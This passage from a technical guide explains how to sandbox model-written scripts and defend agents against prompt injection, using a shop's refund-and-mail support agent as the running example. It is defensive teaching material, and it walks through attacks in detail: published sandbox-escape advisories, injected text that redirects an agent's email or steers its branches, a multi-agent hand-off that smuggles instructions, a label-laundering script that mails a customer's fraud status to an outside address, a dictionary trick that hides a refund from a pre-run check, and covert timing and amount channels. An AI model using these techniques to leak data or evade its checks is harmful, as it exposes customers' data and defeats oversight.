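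Exposing an object can also expose the objects its methods return, which is easy to overlook. If `ticket.customer()` returned a customer object with a list of orders, and each order had a `refund` method, a developer who meant to expose only the ticket would also expose refunds for all of that customer's orders. Monty prevents this by default because it does not convert a returned object unless the developer has specified how to wrap it. In Starlark in Go, the developer decides how each host type handles attributes. A ready-made converter that exposes every public field and method of a Go value saves work, but it also exposes everything reachable through them.

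In Miller's model, a program can obtain a new reference only by creating an object or receiving one through a reference it already has. A script can therefore reach any object it can get to by following attributes and return values from the host's objects. Miller's "membrane" pattern controls this access by wrapping every object that crosses the boundary in either direction, so that all the wrappers can be disabled at once. It does not wrap plain data, because the host cannot take back data the script has already read.

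### Two sandboxes that exposed too much

Two security advisories from 2026 show how exposing a single object can defeat a sandbox. GitLab's *CVE-2026-25905* (2026) concerns mcp-run-python, a Pydantic project that let models run Python through an MCP server. It used Pyodide, a version of Python that runs inside a JavaScript program, and gave scripts access to a Pyodide module that lets Python code use JavaScript objects.

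A script could therefore change the JavaScript program that was running it. GitLab warns that an attacker could replace one of the server's other tools, such as a function for reading files, with a version that also sent the contents elsewhere, and the server would still appear to work normally. GitLab calls the flaw critical, though its score of 5.8 out of 10 counts as medium. The flaw affected every version up to 0.0.22, and GitLab still listed no fix in May 2026.

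Agenta, a platform for developing applications that use language models, let users submit Python code to evaluate a model's answers. The server ran that code under RestrictedPython, a filter for CPython, and Agenta's developers put the numerical library numpy on the list of safe packages. This created a flaw, recorded as CVE-2026-27952. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-6* (2026), numpy contains a reference to Python's tools for inspecting running programs, and submitted code could use those tools to reach functions that run commands on the server.

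Any user with an account could exploit the flaw, which OSV rates 9.9 out of 10 for severity. Agenta first fixed it in version 0.48.1 by removing numpy from the list, and later replaced the RestrictedPython sandbox.

These cases are evidence about choosing what to expose, not about flaws in Starlark or Monty, because neither product used a hermetic language. numpy is a respected library, but its developers wrote it for programs that already have full access to Python, so they had no reason to hide the modules it uses. Someone who thinks of numpy as a collection of mathematical functions could overlook this. A host that wants to offer scripts an average or a standard deviation can write its own functions that accept a list of numbers and return a number.

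### Passwords, paths and error messages

A host can keep its credentials out of the script and still reveal them in a result. If `orders` is the payment service's own client object, it may have an attribute that holds the key. A stored photo may come with a temporary URL that lets anyone who has it download the file. To prevent this, `tickets.read` should return a new dictionary with only the fields that scripts need. If it converts the whole database record, scripts will also receive any column added later.

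File paths reveal smaller details. Monty gives scripts only virtual paths, which do not show where the host stores the files. In shac, `ctx.scm.root` gives a script the project's full path on the machine, which often includes the developer's user name. A build tool may need the full path, but the support agent does not.

Developers often take less care over error messages than over results. A database library may include the server's address or the text of a query in its errors, and a network library may include a request together with its password. A Monty script can catch the error and read it. Although a Starlark script can't, the host usually sends the message to the model so that it can correct its code. The model might then repeat the details in an email to a customer.

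The Go function `refund` above therefore replaces the payment service's error with "refund failed". The host should write the original error to a log that scripts and models cannot read. It should still explain errors caused by the script's own arguments, such as a negative amount, so that the model can more easily fix its mistakes.

Differences between error messages can also reveal information. If the general `orders.refund` returned "no such order" for some order numbers and "order belongs to another customer" for others, a script could try many numbers and learn which orders exist. The function should return the same message in both cases.

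### Reviewing a proposed host function

Suppose a developer at the shop proposes `orders.find(email)`, which returns a customer's earlier orders, so that scripts can check whether the customer has complained before. A reviewer can work through these steps:

1. Assume that an attacker chooses every argument and calls the function as often as the limits allow, then write down the worst result. With `orders.find`, a script could try many addresses and collect the order history of every customer it guesses.
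2. Read the function's code and find out what it can reach. If it writes anything, find the programs that later read and act on it.
3. Look for arguments that name something, such as an address, an order number or a path. If the host already knows the right value, remove the argument. Here the host knows which customer the ticket belongs to, so the function can become `past_orders()`.
4. If the script has to choose, let it choose from a list that the host prepared for this request.
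5. Check the remaining arguments at the start of the function. Test it with negative numbers, very large numbers, empty text and values of the wrong type.
6. Decide which fields the result needs. To check for earlier complaints, a script needs dates and complaint codes, but not card details or delivery addresses. If the result contains objects, follow their attributes and methods too.
7. Cause each error deliberately and read what the script and the model receive.
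8. Check that the function counts its memory and stops when the host cancels the script. If it changes anything, decide what should happen when a script calls it twice.
9. Decide when the function stops working, and test that it does.
10. Consider what a script could do with this function and those it already has, since several safe functions can cause harm together.
11. Repeat the review when anyone changes the function or upgrades a library whose objects it returns, because a new version may add methods that scripts can call.

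## Controlling what permitted calls do together

A host function can pass every step of that review and still do harm in combination with another. The shop's staff need `tickets.read` to see complaints and `mail.send` to answer them. This script uses both as their developer intended:

```python
recipient = tickets.read(4471)["customer_email"]
complaint = tickets.read(4460)["message"]
mail.send(recipient, complaint)
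```

A generated program could mail one customer's complaint to another customer. Starlark has no rule against this, and a host rule that allows mail only to customers would not prevent it, because the recipient is a customer.

Bifrost's default limits of 64 tool calls per script and 1 MiB per value cap the damage. A script could read 63 tickets and email them all to one address with its last call, if they averaged no more than about 16 KiB each. Pairing 32 reads with 32 emails would leak the most data, up to 32 MiB. Most complaints are short, so a script could more realistically expose 63 customers, and twenty such scripts could expose 1,260. Lowering the call limit would not help much, since the script above makes only three calls, the same number as the legitimate support script.

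Permitted calls can combine to cause harm even without an attacker. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) describe a user who asks an agent to set up a project by copying a configuration file from an older one, then asks it to publish the project on GitHub. The file contains a private key, which the agent publishes with the project. They observed this with Claude 4.5 Haiku. A fixed rule against network access would have prevented it, but users who need to publish things would soon turn the rule off.

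If the host gives the script one ticket and a function that writes only to that ticket's customer, the script has nothing to leak. But some tasks need broader access. If a member of staff asks the model to send the courier the details of ten damaged parcels, the script has to handle ten customers' data and write to someone who is not a customer.

### Labels that travel with the data

The host could allow the courier's email and refuse the leak if it knew where each piece of text came from and who may see it. Information-flow control attaches this knowledge to values as labels and updates the labels as a program computes. Two labels are enough here. A value's sources are the places its content came from, and its readers are the people who may see it. When a script computes `z` from `x` and `y`, the interpreter combines their labels:

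```
sources(z) = sources(x) ∪ sources(y)
readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
```

A value made by combining two others keeps the sources of both, and only people who may read both may read it. For example, if Ana wrote ticket 4471 and Ben wrote ticket 4460, a value that combines the tickets has both Ana and Ben as sources.

| Text in the script | Readers |
|---|---|
| Ana's message | Staff, Ana |
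| Ben's message | Staff, Ben |
| Both messages joined together | Staff |
| "We have refunded your order in full." | Anyone |

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) describes two rules as sufficient for most practical cases. The "permitted flow" rule allows a call to send data only if every recipient is allowed to read it. Ana isn't allowed to read Ben's message, so the rule blocks the three-line script. The "trusted action" rule allows a call only if the decision to make it was based on trusted information and the arguments that matter came from trusted sources. It would block a refund if the amount came from text the customer typed.

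The shop would have to add the courier to the readers of the delivery address and the order number, but not of the customer's message. Someone has to make such decisions for every field, and a mistake either leaks data or blocks legitimate work.

Joining two strings in an ordinary interpreter produces a new string with no record of its parts, so applying these rules requires an interpreter with tracking built in. A host without one can keep a single, cruder label for the whole script. Once a script has read both Ana's and Ben's tickets, the host lets it write only to staff. This stops the leak however the script rearranges the text, but it also blocks a script that refunds thirty customers and writes to each one. The host could run that job as thirty scripts with one ticket each, provided that the model does not carry text from one script to the next.

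### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., Google DeepMind, 2025) presents CaMeL, a system that runs model-written code in an interpreter with per-value tracking. CaMeL extends a two-model design that Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request and plans the work, while a quarantined model with no tools reads the untrusted data, which the privileged model never sees.

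Separating the models stops hostile text from adding steps to the plan. It does not stop the text from changing the data that the steps use, a flaw in his own design that Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, says the DeepMind paper showed him. Suppose a staff member asks the model to write to the courier whose address is in ticket 4471:

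```python
ticket = tickets.read(4471)
address = ask_quarantined("Find the courier's address", ticket["message"])
mail.send(address, "Please collect order " + ticket["order_id"])
```

The customer's message could contain an instruction to return a different address. The plan would not change, but the email would go to the attacker.

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes its plan in a restricted form of Python, which a custom interpreter executes by walking the syntax tree. The interpreter labels every value with a set of sources and a set of readers. Here it records that `address` depends on the customer's message. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, an ordinary Python function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels. The policy either allows the call or denies it with a reason. A policy for `mail.send` could deny this call because the recipient came from untrusted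 text, and the system could then ask the staff member to confirm the address.

Several groups have since tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates banking, travel, office and messaging tasks and plants hostile instructions in the data. In a run for *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of 97 ordinary tasks. *AgentSys* (2026) also reports no successful attacks, with 30% of ordinary tasks completed. Both papers propose competing defences, so their researchers lacked the incentive CaMeL's developers have to make it perform well.

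In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) also propose a competitor to CaMeL, but they tested CaMeL with its policies on and off, which shows what the policies and the rest of the system each contribute. They ran 16 banking tasks three times each with two models. The attack figures cover only the runs that finished.

| Model | Policies | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
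|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Off | 1 of 240 | 32 of 48 |
| GPT-5.2 | On | 0 of 231 | 18 of 48 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 4 of 382 | 34 of 48 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | On | 0 of 357 | 18 of 48 |

The policies stopped the last 1% of attacks and nearly halved the number of completed tasks. The benefit looks small partly because of the choice of attacks. In about two-thirds of the task-attack pairs, the attack needs a tool call that the plan for the user's task would never contain, so separating the models defeats it without any policy. Leaking a ticket, however, needs only calls that a legitimate script also makes. A shop worried about that leak would benefit more from the policies than the results in the table indicate.

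CaMeL also uses more tokens than an undefended agent. On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) measured 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens for the median task.

Kolluri and colleagues object to how evaluations usually count lost tasks. Evaluations normally treat a blocked call as a failure, while letting the undefended agent do anything without permission. In practice, many agents ask a person before every consequential action. An agent that tracks labels can ask less often, because it needs a person only when a call breaks a policy. In their AgentDojo tests, basic tracking reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.5, and the agent completed no fewer tasks. These tests were simulations that assumed the person would approve every request in a successful run.

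### Gaps in the tracking

Labels also have to account for decisions. If a script sends an email only when a ticket's status is "suspected fraud", the email reveals the status even if its text is a single harmless word. CaMeL handles the simple case by treating a call inside such an `if` statement as dependent on the secret. Garby and colleagues show that a longer script can get around this, using a trick that researchers have known since the 1970s. In the shop's terms, it looks like this:

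```python
flagged = True
clear = True
if ticket["status"] == "suspected fraud":
    clear = False
if clear:
    flagged = False
if flagged:
    mail.send("stranger@mail.example", "yes")
```

If the customer is under suspicion, the script sets `clear` to `False`, and the interpreter labels `clear` as secret. The interpreter then skips the line `flagged = False`, so it never labels `flagged`. The last `if` therefore appears to depend on nothing secret, and the email goes out. If the customer is not under suspicion, no email goes out, so the stranger learns the status either way.

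CaMeL's privileged model ordinarily has no reason to write such code, and hostile text in a ticket cannot reach it. The trick matters if the model has an aim of its own, or if an attacker can influence the original request. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists CaMeL's trust in that request as one of its main gaps. Garby and colleagues close the leak with a language whose label rules they proved correct in a proof assistant. Their agent resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. Both failures came from a task that told the agent to read a file and make whatever payment it specified, after the attacker had replaced the file. If a staff member tells the model to do what a customer's email asks, labels cannot distinguish a legitimate request from a fraudulent one.

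CaMeL's policies also look at only one call at a time. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, add a check of the whole plan before it runs. Their program converts the plan into a diagram of possible states, in which each `if` becomes a fork and each loop may repeat any number of times. A model checker, a tool that explores all such paths, then looks for one that breaks a rule. The shop could require a message to the customer after every refund:

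```
AG(call_refund ⇒ AF(call_mail))
```

`AG` means "at every point on every path" and `AF` means "eventually, on every path from here". A script that would refund an order and return without writing to the customer fails the check before any money moves. The checker also reports the path that violates the rule, which the model can use to correct its plan.

In a test with seven deliberately unsafe plans for a security team, CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The large gap is unsurprising, because Nikolaou and colleagues chose the rules to go beyond what CaMeL can express. CaMeLoT also reproduced 22 of 28 CaMeL policies for AgentDojo without running anything. It leaves rules about who may read data to CaMeL, because a document's permitted readers are often unknown until the script fetches it. The ticket leak would therefore still need a check when the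 call is made. CaMeLoT can confirm that a script calls `mail.send` after each refund, but not that the mail server will be working.

Labels can disappear when a script hands text to another agent. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked it to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack. One agent fetched the applicants' records from a database, where the researchers had hidden an instruction to email the records to an outside address. The coordinating agent pasted the summary into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its privileged model read the hidden instruction and added the email to its plan.

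They propose passing instructions and data separately, so that the receiving agent's privileged model sees only the instructions. On a benchmark they built, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with the new protocol. A host that lets scripts call another agent should likewise give the function that makes the call one argument for fixed instructions and another for data.

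### Values a script can carry but not read

A host can also hide data from a script by giving it an opaque value, a token that stands for the data. The script can pass the token to host functions but cannot print it, compare it or take it apart. Flyte, a workflow system from Union.ai that runs model-written code on Monty, uses opaque values for files, directories and data tables. According to Union.ai's *Sandboxing*, a script can pass them between tasks but cannot inspect them.

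If `tickets.read` returned the customer's message as an opaque value, the script could not copy a sentence from it into an email to someone else, or print it where the model would read it. The interpreter would not need to propagate labels to derived values, since the script could not compute anything from the message. But the script could still pass the opaque value to `mail.send` with the wrong address, so that host function would have to look up who may read the message and refuse other recipients.

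Opaque values become less protective once a script needs to act on their content. The usual solution is a host function that asks a quarantined model to choose from a fixed list:

```python
kind = classify(ticket["message"], ["damaged", "late", "other"])
if kind == "damaged":
    refund(ticket["amount_paid"])
elif kind == "late":
    notify("Your parcel is on its way.")
```

As with Baya's model calls, hostile text cannot add a call here, but it can still influence the answer and so select the branch that pays. A choice among *n* categories gives hostile text up to log₂ *n* bits of control, which is 1.6 bits here. Ten choices, each among eight categories, would give it up to 30 bits, enough to select any of about a billion paths through a script.

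*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) calls this attack branch steering and demonstrates it on agents that operate a web browser. The planner writes a complete program in advance, with branches for situations such as a cookie notice covering the page. In the demonstration, an advertisement contained a fake cookie notice. The agent followed its plan for closing cookie notices, clicked, and landed on the attacker's site. As a defense, the paper tried comparing the answers of independent models, but this only makes the attack less likely. Clicks also have no fixed meaning that a policy could check. The shop is easier to protect because `refund` always means the same thing and can itself check that staff have confirmed the damage.

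A reviewer should therefore assume that the customer chooses every branch that depends on a classification, and ask whether each branch would be acceptable. Loops need special care. In one of Garby and colleagues' tests, CaMeL was asked to follow a file's instructions precisely, and its privileged model wrote a loop that read the next instruction, classified it and called the matching tool. With the policies off, the file's author could then make any of those calls in any order, as if the two models had not been separated.

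### Leaks without a channel

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asked how someone could let another person's program process confidential data and be sure that it passed nothing on. Blocking files and messages is not enough, because the program could encode data in the bill it sends for its services. It could also lock and unlock a file while another program checks whether it is available, or vary how hard it works the machine while another program measures the slowdown. Lampson called this last kind of route a covert channel, because nobody intended it to carry information.

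A script can leak data in similar ways. Suppose it can see another customer's record, and its only way to affect the outside world is to refund Ana between 1 and 4,500 cents. Its choice of amount can carry about 12 bits, enough for the last three digits of the other customer's phone number. If the script has to send ten routine emails, their order can carry about 21 bits. Even stopping with an error can reveal information to anyone who sees that the job failed.

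Determinism and a frozen clock close some of these routes. With the clock frozen, a script cannot time `tickets.read` to work out whether a colleague has just opened the same ticket. It cannot pass off a signal as random variation either, because it has no random numbers. If a refund of $12.34 looks odd, a reviewer can rerun the script on the same inputs and trace how it computed the amount.

A script without a clock can still send information through the timing of its calls, because people outside the sandbox do have clocks. It could run a long loop before calling `mail.send` to mean "yes", or call it immediately to mean "no", and the recipient could tell which from the arrival time. A step limit shortens the possible delay, and a host that collects outgoing mail and sends it at fixed times removes most of the signal. A host function can also accidentally give the script a clock, for example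 by returning the time when the mail server accepted a message.

Small leaks add up when a script can run repeatedly. Garby and colleagues point out that CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop, and that whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret. Each attempt reveals one bit, so twenty are enough to identify one order number out of a million. A host should count refusals across the whole request and stop after a few.

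The risk of a script leaking a secret through refund amounts depends on the secret's length. A 2,000-character complaint is about 16,000 bits as plain text, so leaking it would take more than 1,300 refunds. A key, a card number or the answer to a yes-or-no question could leak in far fewer. The shop should first stop scripts from emailing data directly to the wrong person, and should never give scripts access to short secrets.

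### Approving a script or approving a call

When no rule can settle whether an action is right, the host can ask a person. Bifrost's documentation describes its search for calls outside the operator's list for automatic use as a heuristic, because the search recognises only calls written in the form `server.tool(...)`. Suppose the operator lets scripts read tickets and send mail unattended, but not pay refunds. This script contains no refund in that form:

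```python
actions = {"tell": mail.send, "repay": orders.refund}
actions["repay"](order_id="A-1093", amount=4500)
```

The search finds no problem, so the script starts. When it reaches the second line, Bifrost checks the tool again and refuses the call. The documentation describes only this second check as a guarantee, because it examines the tool the script is about to use, however the script refers to it. If a plugin renames the tool during the call, Bifrost checks the new name.

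The search is still useful because it can stop a script before it does anything, whereas refusing a call when the script makes it may happen after the script has, for example, sent three emails.

Bifrost treats a person's approval of a script as permission for everything in it. It stops checking calls against the list of tools allowed for automatic use, but still blocks tools that the operator has disabled altogether. Someone who approved the script above without noticing the dictionary would have approved the refund. Both checks cover only which tools a script calls, not what the calls do together. With `tickets.read` and `mail.send` on the list, the script that mails Ben's complaint to Ana would pass both checks without anyone being asked to approve it.

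A person can approve a script in advance or approve each call as it happens. If they approve the script in advance, they see code such as `orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], ticket["amount_paid"])`, but not the order or the amount. If they approve each call, they see the actual request, such as a $45 refund on order A-1093, but the script may already have taken other actions. Most support staff could judge a specific refund better than they could judge the code.

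Willison worries that people who have to approve many actions will start saying yes to everything, and Adam and colleagues add that approval prompts rely on the user understanding the consequences of, say, a shell command. Kolluri and colleagues reduce the number of prompts by letting the user approve data. If a trusted colleague's email contains ten tasks, the user can read it once and mark it as trusted, and the agent then carries out all ten without asking again. Their agent, Prudentia, also plans its work to avoid breaking policies. It cut the number of approvals by a factor of up to 1.9 on AgentDojo. The user has to read the email carefully, though, because approving it also approves any instruction an attacker has hidden in it.

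### Waiting for the answer

A host that uses Pydantic's Monty can pause a script halfway through for a manager's approval and save its state overnight. Flyte uses the same pause for slow work. It stops the script at each external call, runs the task in a container, and resumes the script with the result.

The host should store the exact call and its arguments with the saved state, so that the manager's approval covers only a refund of $45 on order A-1093. During the wait, a colleague may have refunded the order by hand or changed the ticket's status. The saved script's copy of the ticket dates from the evening before and does not include these changes, so `refund` has to check the current status when it runs.

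Saved state is also easy to copy. If two servers load the same file after the manager clicks "approve", each can resume the script and pay the refund. Before it resumes a script, the host should mark the saved state as used in a single database transaction.

### Scripts that stop halfway

If a script fails at its fifth call, it has already made four, and discarding the script does not undo them. A database can cancel a group of changes if one fails, but a payment and an email go to separate systems that share no such mechanism. The shop could ask the customer to return the money, but it cannot take back the email once it is sent.

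Some failures do not even stop the script. Bifrost departs from Starlark's usual behaviour: when a connected tool reports a failure, it gives the script an error value and carries on with the next line. The support script ignores what `orders.refund` returns, so under Bifrost it would tell the customer "We have refunded your order in full" after a refund that failed. It needs an explicit check:

```python
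r = orders.refund(order_id=ticket["order_id"], amount=ticket["amount_paid"])
if hasattr(r, "error"):
    fail(r.error)
```

A timeout is harder to handle, because the host cannot tell whether a retry is safe. Four techniques together solve most of the problem:

- **Recorded results.** The host writes down each call before making it, and writes down the result afterwards.
- **Replay.** The host runs the same script again but returns the recorded results instead of repeating the calls. This works only if the script is deterministic, since it has to make the same calls in the same order.
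- **Dry run.** The host lets the script read real data but replaces every function that changes something with one that only notes the request.
- **Idempotency key.** The host attaches a unique identifier to a request. If the payment service receives the same identifier twice, it pays once and returns the original answer both times.

### A trace of one request

A member of staff asks the model to refund tickets 4471 and 4472 if the damage is confirmed, and to tell both customers. The model writes:

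```python
def handle(ticket_ids):
    for ticket_id in ticket_ids:
        ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)
        if ticket["status"] == "damage confirmed":
            orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], ticket["amount_paid"])
            mail.send(ticket["customer_email"],
                      "We have refunded your order in full.")

handle([4471, 4472])
```

The host runs the script three times. The dry run produces a list of two refunds and two emails, with real amounts and addresses, and the staff member approves it. In the live run, the payment service pays the second refund but its response never arrives, so the script stops. The host then replays the script to finish the job.

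| Call | Dry run | Live run | Replay |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Read ticket 4471 | Reads and records it | Uses the record | Uses the record |
| 2. Refund A-1093, $45 | Notes the request | Pays, records success | Uses the record |
| 3. Email the first customer | Notes the request | Sends, records success | Uses the record |
| 4. Read ticket 4472 | Reads and records it | Uses the record | Uses the record |
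| 5. Refund A-1101, $28 | Notes the request | Times out after the service has paid | Sends the same key, gets the original answer |
| 6. Email the second customer | Notes the request | Never starts | Sends, records success |

Each customer receives one refund and one email. If the host had rerun the script without the record and keys, the shop could have paid an extra $73 and emailed the first customer twice.

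The live run reuses the tickets recorded in the dry run so that it follows the path the staff member approved. At each call, the host compares the function and arguments with the approved list and stops the run if they differ. These tickets may be out of date by then, which is another reason for `orders.refund` to check the current status itself.

A dry run is reliable only if the substitutes behave like the real functions. `orders.refund` returns nothing, so it is easy to replace. If it returned a receipt number that the script put in the email, the substitute would have to invent one, and the approved email would not match the real one. The host also has to know which functions only read data. A function that fetches a web address can send a customer's data to a stranger during the dry run, even though it looks like a read.

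The payment service has to support idempotency keys. Most mail servers don't support them, so if the host crashes after sending an email but before recording it, it cannot determine whether the customer received the message. It has to either resend the email and risk a duplicate, or not resend it and risk the customer never receiving it. For a refund notice, a duplicate is less of a problem than a missing message.

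A refund's idempotency key should also stay the same when the model writes a new script after an error. If the host builds each key from the call's position, the refund for A-1101 might be the fifth call in the old script and the second in the new one, and the payment service would treat them as two different requests. A key built from the staff member's request and the order number would be the same in both scripts, but it would also merge two partial refunds that the staff member wanted to make on the same order. The host therefore needs a separate identifier for each refund the staff member approves.

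## Getting a model to write the dialect

A model asked for a support script will probably write ordinary Python, because models learn from far more Python than Starlark. Most public Starlark is build files, which are not much like a program that reads a ticket and pays a refund. Varda and Pai claim that code mode works because models are familiar with real code. They give no measurements, but if they are right, a rarer dialect loses part of the benefit.

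When Pydantic introduced Monty, it published a script that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had written to compare the weather in London and Paris. The script begins with `await asyncio.gather(...)`, which starts two calls at once, and ends with a dictionary on its own line, the way people end a notebook cell to display a value. Monty accepts both of these Python habits. Starlark reserves the word `await`, so it would reject the script before making any call. A model that then removed the `await` might keep the ending, and Starlark would build the dictionary and discard it. Bifrost returns only what a script prints or assigns to `result`, so the model would receive nothing, even though the script finished without an error.

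### Loud and silent differences

According to Bazel, when Starlark behaves differently from Python, it usually does so by raising an error. If the host has side effects, when the error occurs also matters. The table shows the Go version's default behaviour, based on the Starlark language definition and Starlark in Go's list of reserved words.

| What a model might write | What Starlark does | When the problem appears |
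|---|---|---|
| `import`, `try`, `with`, `class`, `yield`, `x is None` | Syntax error | Before the script runs |
| `f"Refunded {amount}"` | Syntax error | Before the script runs |
| `0 < amount <= limit` | Syntax error | Before the script runs |
| `{t["order_id"] for t in found}`, which builds a set | Syntax error | Before the script runs |
| `sum(...)`, `round(...)`, `isinstance(...)` | Undefined name | Before the script runs |
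| `while`, or `for` and `if` outside a function | Error, unless the host enables them | Before the script runs |
| `"%.2f" % price` | Error, because `%` cannot set decimal places | During the run |
| `for letter in name` | Error, because scripts cannot loop over a string | During the run |
| A function that calls itself | Error, unless the host enables recursion | During the run |
| `{"a": 1, "a": 2}` | Error, whereas Python keeps the last value | During the run |
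| `type(ticket) == dict` | Always `False`, because `type` returns the text `"dict"` | Never |
| `ticket["refunded"] == 1`, when the field is `True` | `False`, whereas Python gives `True` | Never |
| `queue.popitem()` | Removes the first entry, whereas Python removes the last | Never |
| `message[:100]` | Takes 100 bytes, which may cut an accented letter in half | Never |

Other interpreters differ on some of these rows. The Rust version of Starlark, for example, accepts a limited form of f-string if the host turns it on.

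Few of the differences fail silently, but those that do can be expensive. If the shop's tickets had a boolean `refunded` field and a script used `== 1` to skip customers who had already been refunded, Starlark would skip nobody, because `True == 1` is false in Starlark. The script would try to refund all of them again, and only a check inside `orders.refund` could stop it.

Some of the errors protect the shop from mistakes that Python would let through. Suppose a model writes a loop over a list of addresses but passes it a single address, `"ana@mail.example"`. Python would loop over its characters and call `mail.send` sixteen times, starting with the address "a". Starlark's designers made strings non-iterable to catch this mistake.

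### Converting a Python script

Here is a script that a model might plausibly write for the support agent if nobody mentioned Starlark:

```python
import logging

def refund_ticket(ticket_id):
    try:
        ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)
        if not isinstance(ticket, dict):
            return
        amount = ticket["amount_paid"]
        if ticket["status"] == "damage confirmed" and 0 < amount <= 50000:
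            orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], amount)
            mail.send(ticket["customer_email"],
                      f"We have refunded ${amount / 100:.2f}.")
    except Exception as error:
        logging.error(f"Ticket {ticket_id}: {error}")

for ticket_id in [4471, 4472]:
    refund_ticket(ticket_id)
```

It is reasonable Python, and six parts of it need to change:

| Python | Starlark | Reason |
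|---|---|---|
| `import logging` | Delete it | Scripts cannot import modules |
| `try:` and `except` | Delete them | Scripts cannot catch errors |
| `not isinstance(ticket, dict)` | `type(ticket) != "dict"` | `isinstance` does not exist |
| `0 < amount <= 50000` | `0 < amount and amount <= 50000` | Comparisons do not chain |
| `f"...${amount / 100:.2f}."` | A helper function, `dollars` | No f-strings and no way to set decimal places |
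| `for` at the top level | Put it inside a function | Default rule for loops |

The result is:

```python
def dollars(cents):
    rest = cents % 100
    return "$%d.%s%d" % (cents // 100, "0" if rest < 10 else "", rest)

def refund_ticket(ticket_id):
    ticket = tickets.read(ticket_id)
    if type(ticket) != "dict":
        return
    amount = ticket["amount_paid"]
    if ticket["status"] == "damage confirmed" and 0 < amount and amount <= 50000:
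        orders.refund(ticket["order_id"], amount)
        mail.send(ticket["customer_email"],
                  "We have refunded " + dollars(amount) + ".")

def main():
    for ticket_id in [4471, 4472]:
        refund_ticket(ticket_id)

main()
```

If the interpreter reported only the first syntax error each time, and the model fixed only that one, Starlark would reject at least five versions before running anything. A capable model would probably recognise the dialect from the first error and fix several problems at once.

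Fixing an error that stops the script can introduce a bug that raises no error. A Python programmer who learns that `isinstance` is missing would naturally write `type(ticket) != dict`, without quotation marks around `dict`. In Starlark this comparison is always true, so `refund_ticket` would return at once for every ticket. The script would finish normally without refunding anyone, and the model might tell the member of staff that it had dealt with both customers.

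Starlark has no exact replacement for Python's `try` statement. In the Python version, if the first refund fails, the script logs the error and moves on to ticket 4472. The Starlark version stops, and the second customer gets nothing until someone runs another script. Bifrost's error values let a script either stop or continue after a failure, provided that the model writes code to check them.

### What the benchmarks measure

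Bifrost compared its Starlark-based Code Mode with direct tool calls in three rounds, connecting more tools each time. Both methods answered the same queries within each round.

| Tools connected | Passed, direct calls | Passed, Code Mode | Input tokens, direct calls | Input tokens, Code Mode | Reduction |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 96 | 64 of 64 | 64 of 64 | 19.9 million | 8.3 million | 58.2% |
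| 251 | 64 of 65 | 65 of 65 | 35.7 million | 5.5 million | 84.5% |
| 508 | 65 of 65 | 65 of 65 | 75.1 million | 5.4 million | 92.8% |

In the last round, the estimated cost fell from $377 to $29. Bifrost ran this benchmark on its own product, so a buyer should repeat it with their own queries. The pass rates hardly distinguish the two methods, since direct calls failed only one query out of 194. A query counts as passed whether the first script succeeded or the fifth, so the pass rates also don't measure how many scripts failed before one worked.

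The saving grows mainly because direct calls use more tokens. In Bifrost's baseline, the model receives every tool definition again on every turn, whereas in Code Mode it looks up only the ones it needs. A host could also look up definitions on demand and then make direct calls, so the benchmark does not show how much of the saving comes from writing code. Code Mode also used a third fewer tokens with 251 tools than with 96. Adding tools cannot explain that drop, so something else must have varied between the rounds.

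Red Hat's *Code execution with MCP* reports a smaller reduction in "token overhead", 53%, from one task with 38 tools and Claude Opus. The model wrote full Python rather than a dialect, and the code ran in an isolated sandbox.

| Measure | Direct calls | Sandboxed Python |
|---|---|---|
| Context on the first turn | 41,205 tokens | 26,635 tokens |
| Largest context | 49,697 tokens | 36,518 tokens |
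| Tokens newly stored in the provider's cache | 321,053 | 119,804 |
| Turns | 21 | 25 |
| Tool calls | 10 | 15 |

The first-turn context fell by 35% and the newly cached tokens by 63%, and Red Hat does not show how it arrived at 53%. The similarity to Bifrost's 58.2% for 96 tools means little, because Bifrost counted all input tokens over a whole set of queries. In Red Hat's test, the direct calls all succeeded, whereas the Python version needed five more calls, some to look up tools and some to retry scripts that had failed even though models know Python well.

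One cause was that Gemini Flash called the tool `list-events` by the name `list_events`, which follows Python's naming convention. A host could avoid this error by renaming its tools to match. A Starlark host has to do so anyway if scripts call the tools by name, because Starlark would parse `list-events` as a subtraction.

Pydantic's weather example had only three tools, and code mode saved much less. Input tokens fell from about 4,100 to 3,300, the cost from $0.019 to $0.017, and the time from 12.2 seconds to 9.1. Code mode needed two model calls, and a third call of average size to repair a failed script would have raised the total to about 5,000 tokens, more than the direct calls used. With a few tools, code mode therefore saves tokens only if the first script usually works. With 508 tools, code mode cut Bifrost's average query from 1.15 million tokens to 83,000, so a model could fail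 many times and still use fewer tokens.

The results of these three tests don't include how often a model's first Starlark script failed, so they can't show how much difficulty the dialect itself adds. A host can measure this from its own logs by counting four outcomes for first attempts: the interpreter rejected the script, the script stopped before changing anything, it stopped after changing something, or it finished. Someone then has to read a sample of the finished scripts, because scripts with silent errors are counted as finished.

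### Stubs and a short list of differences

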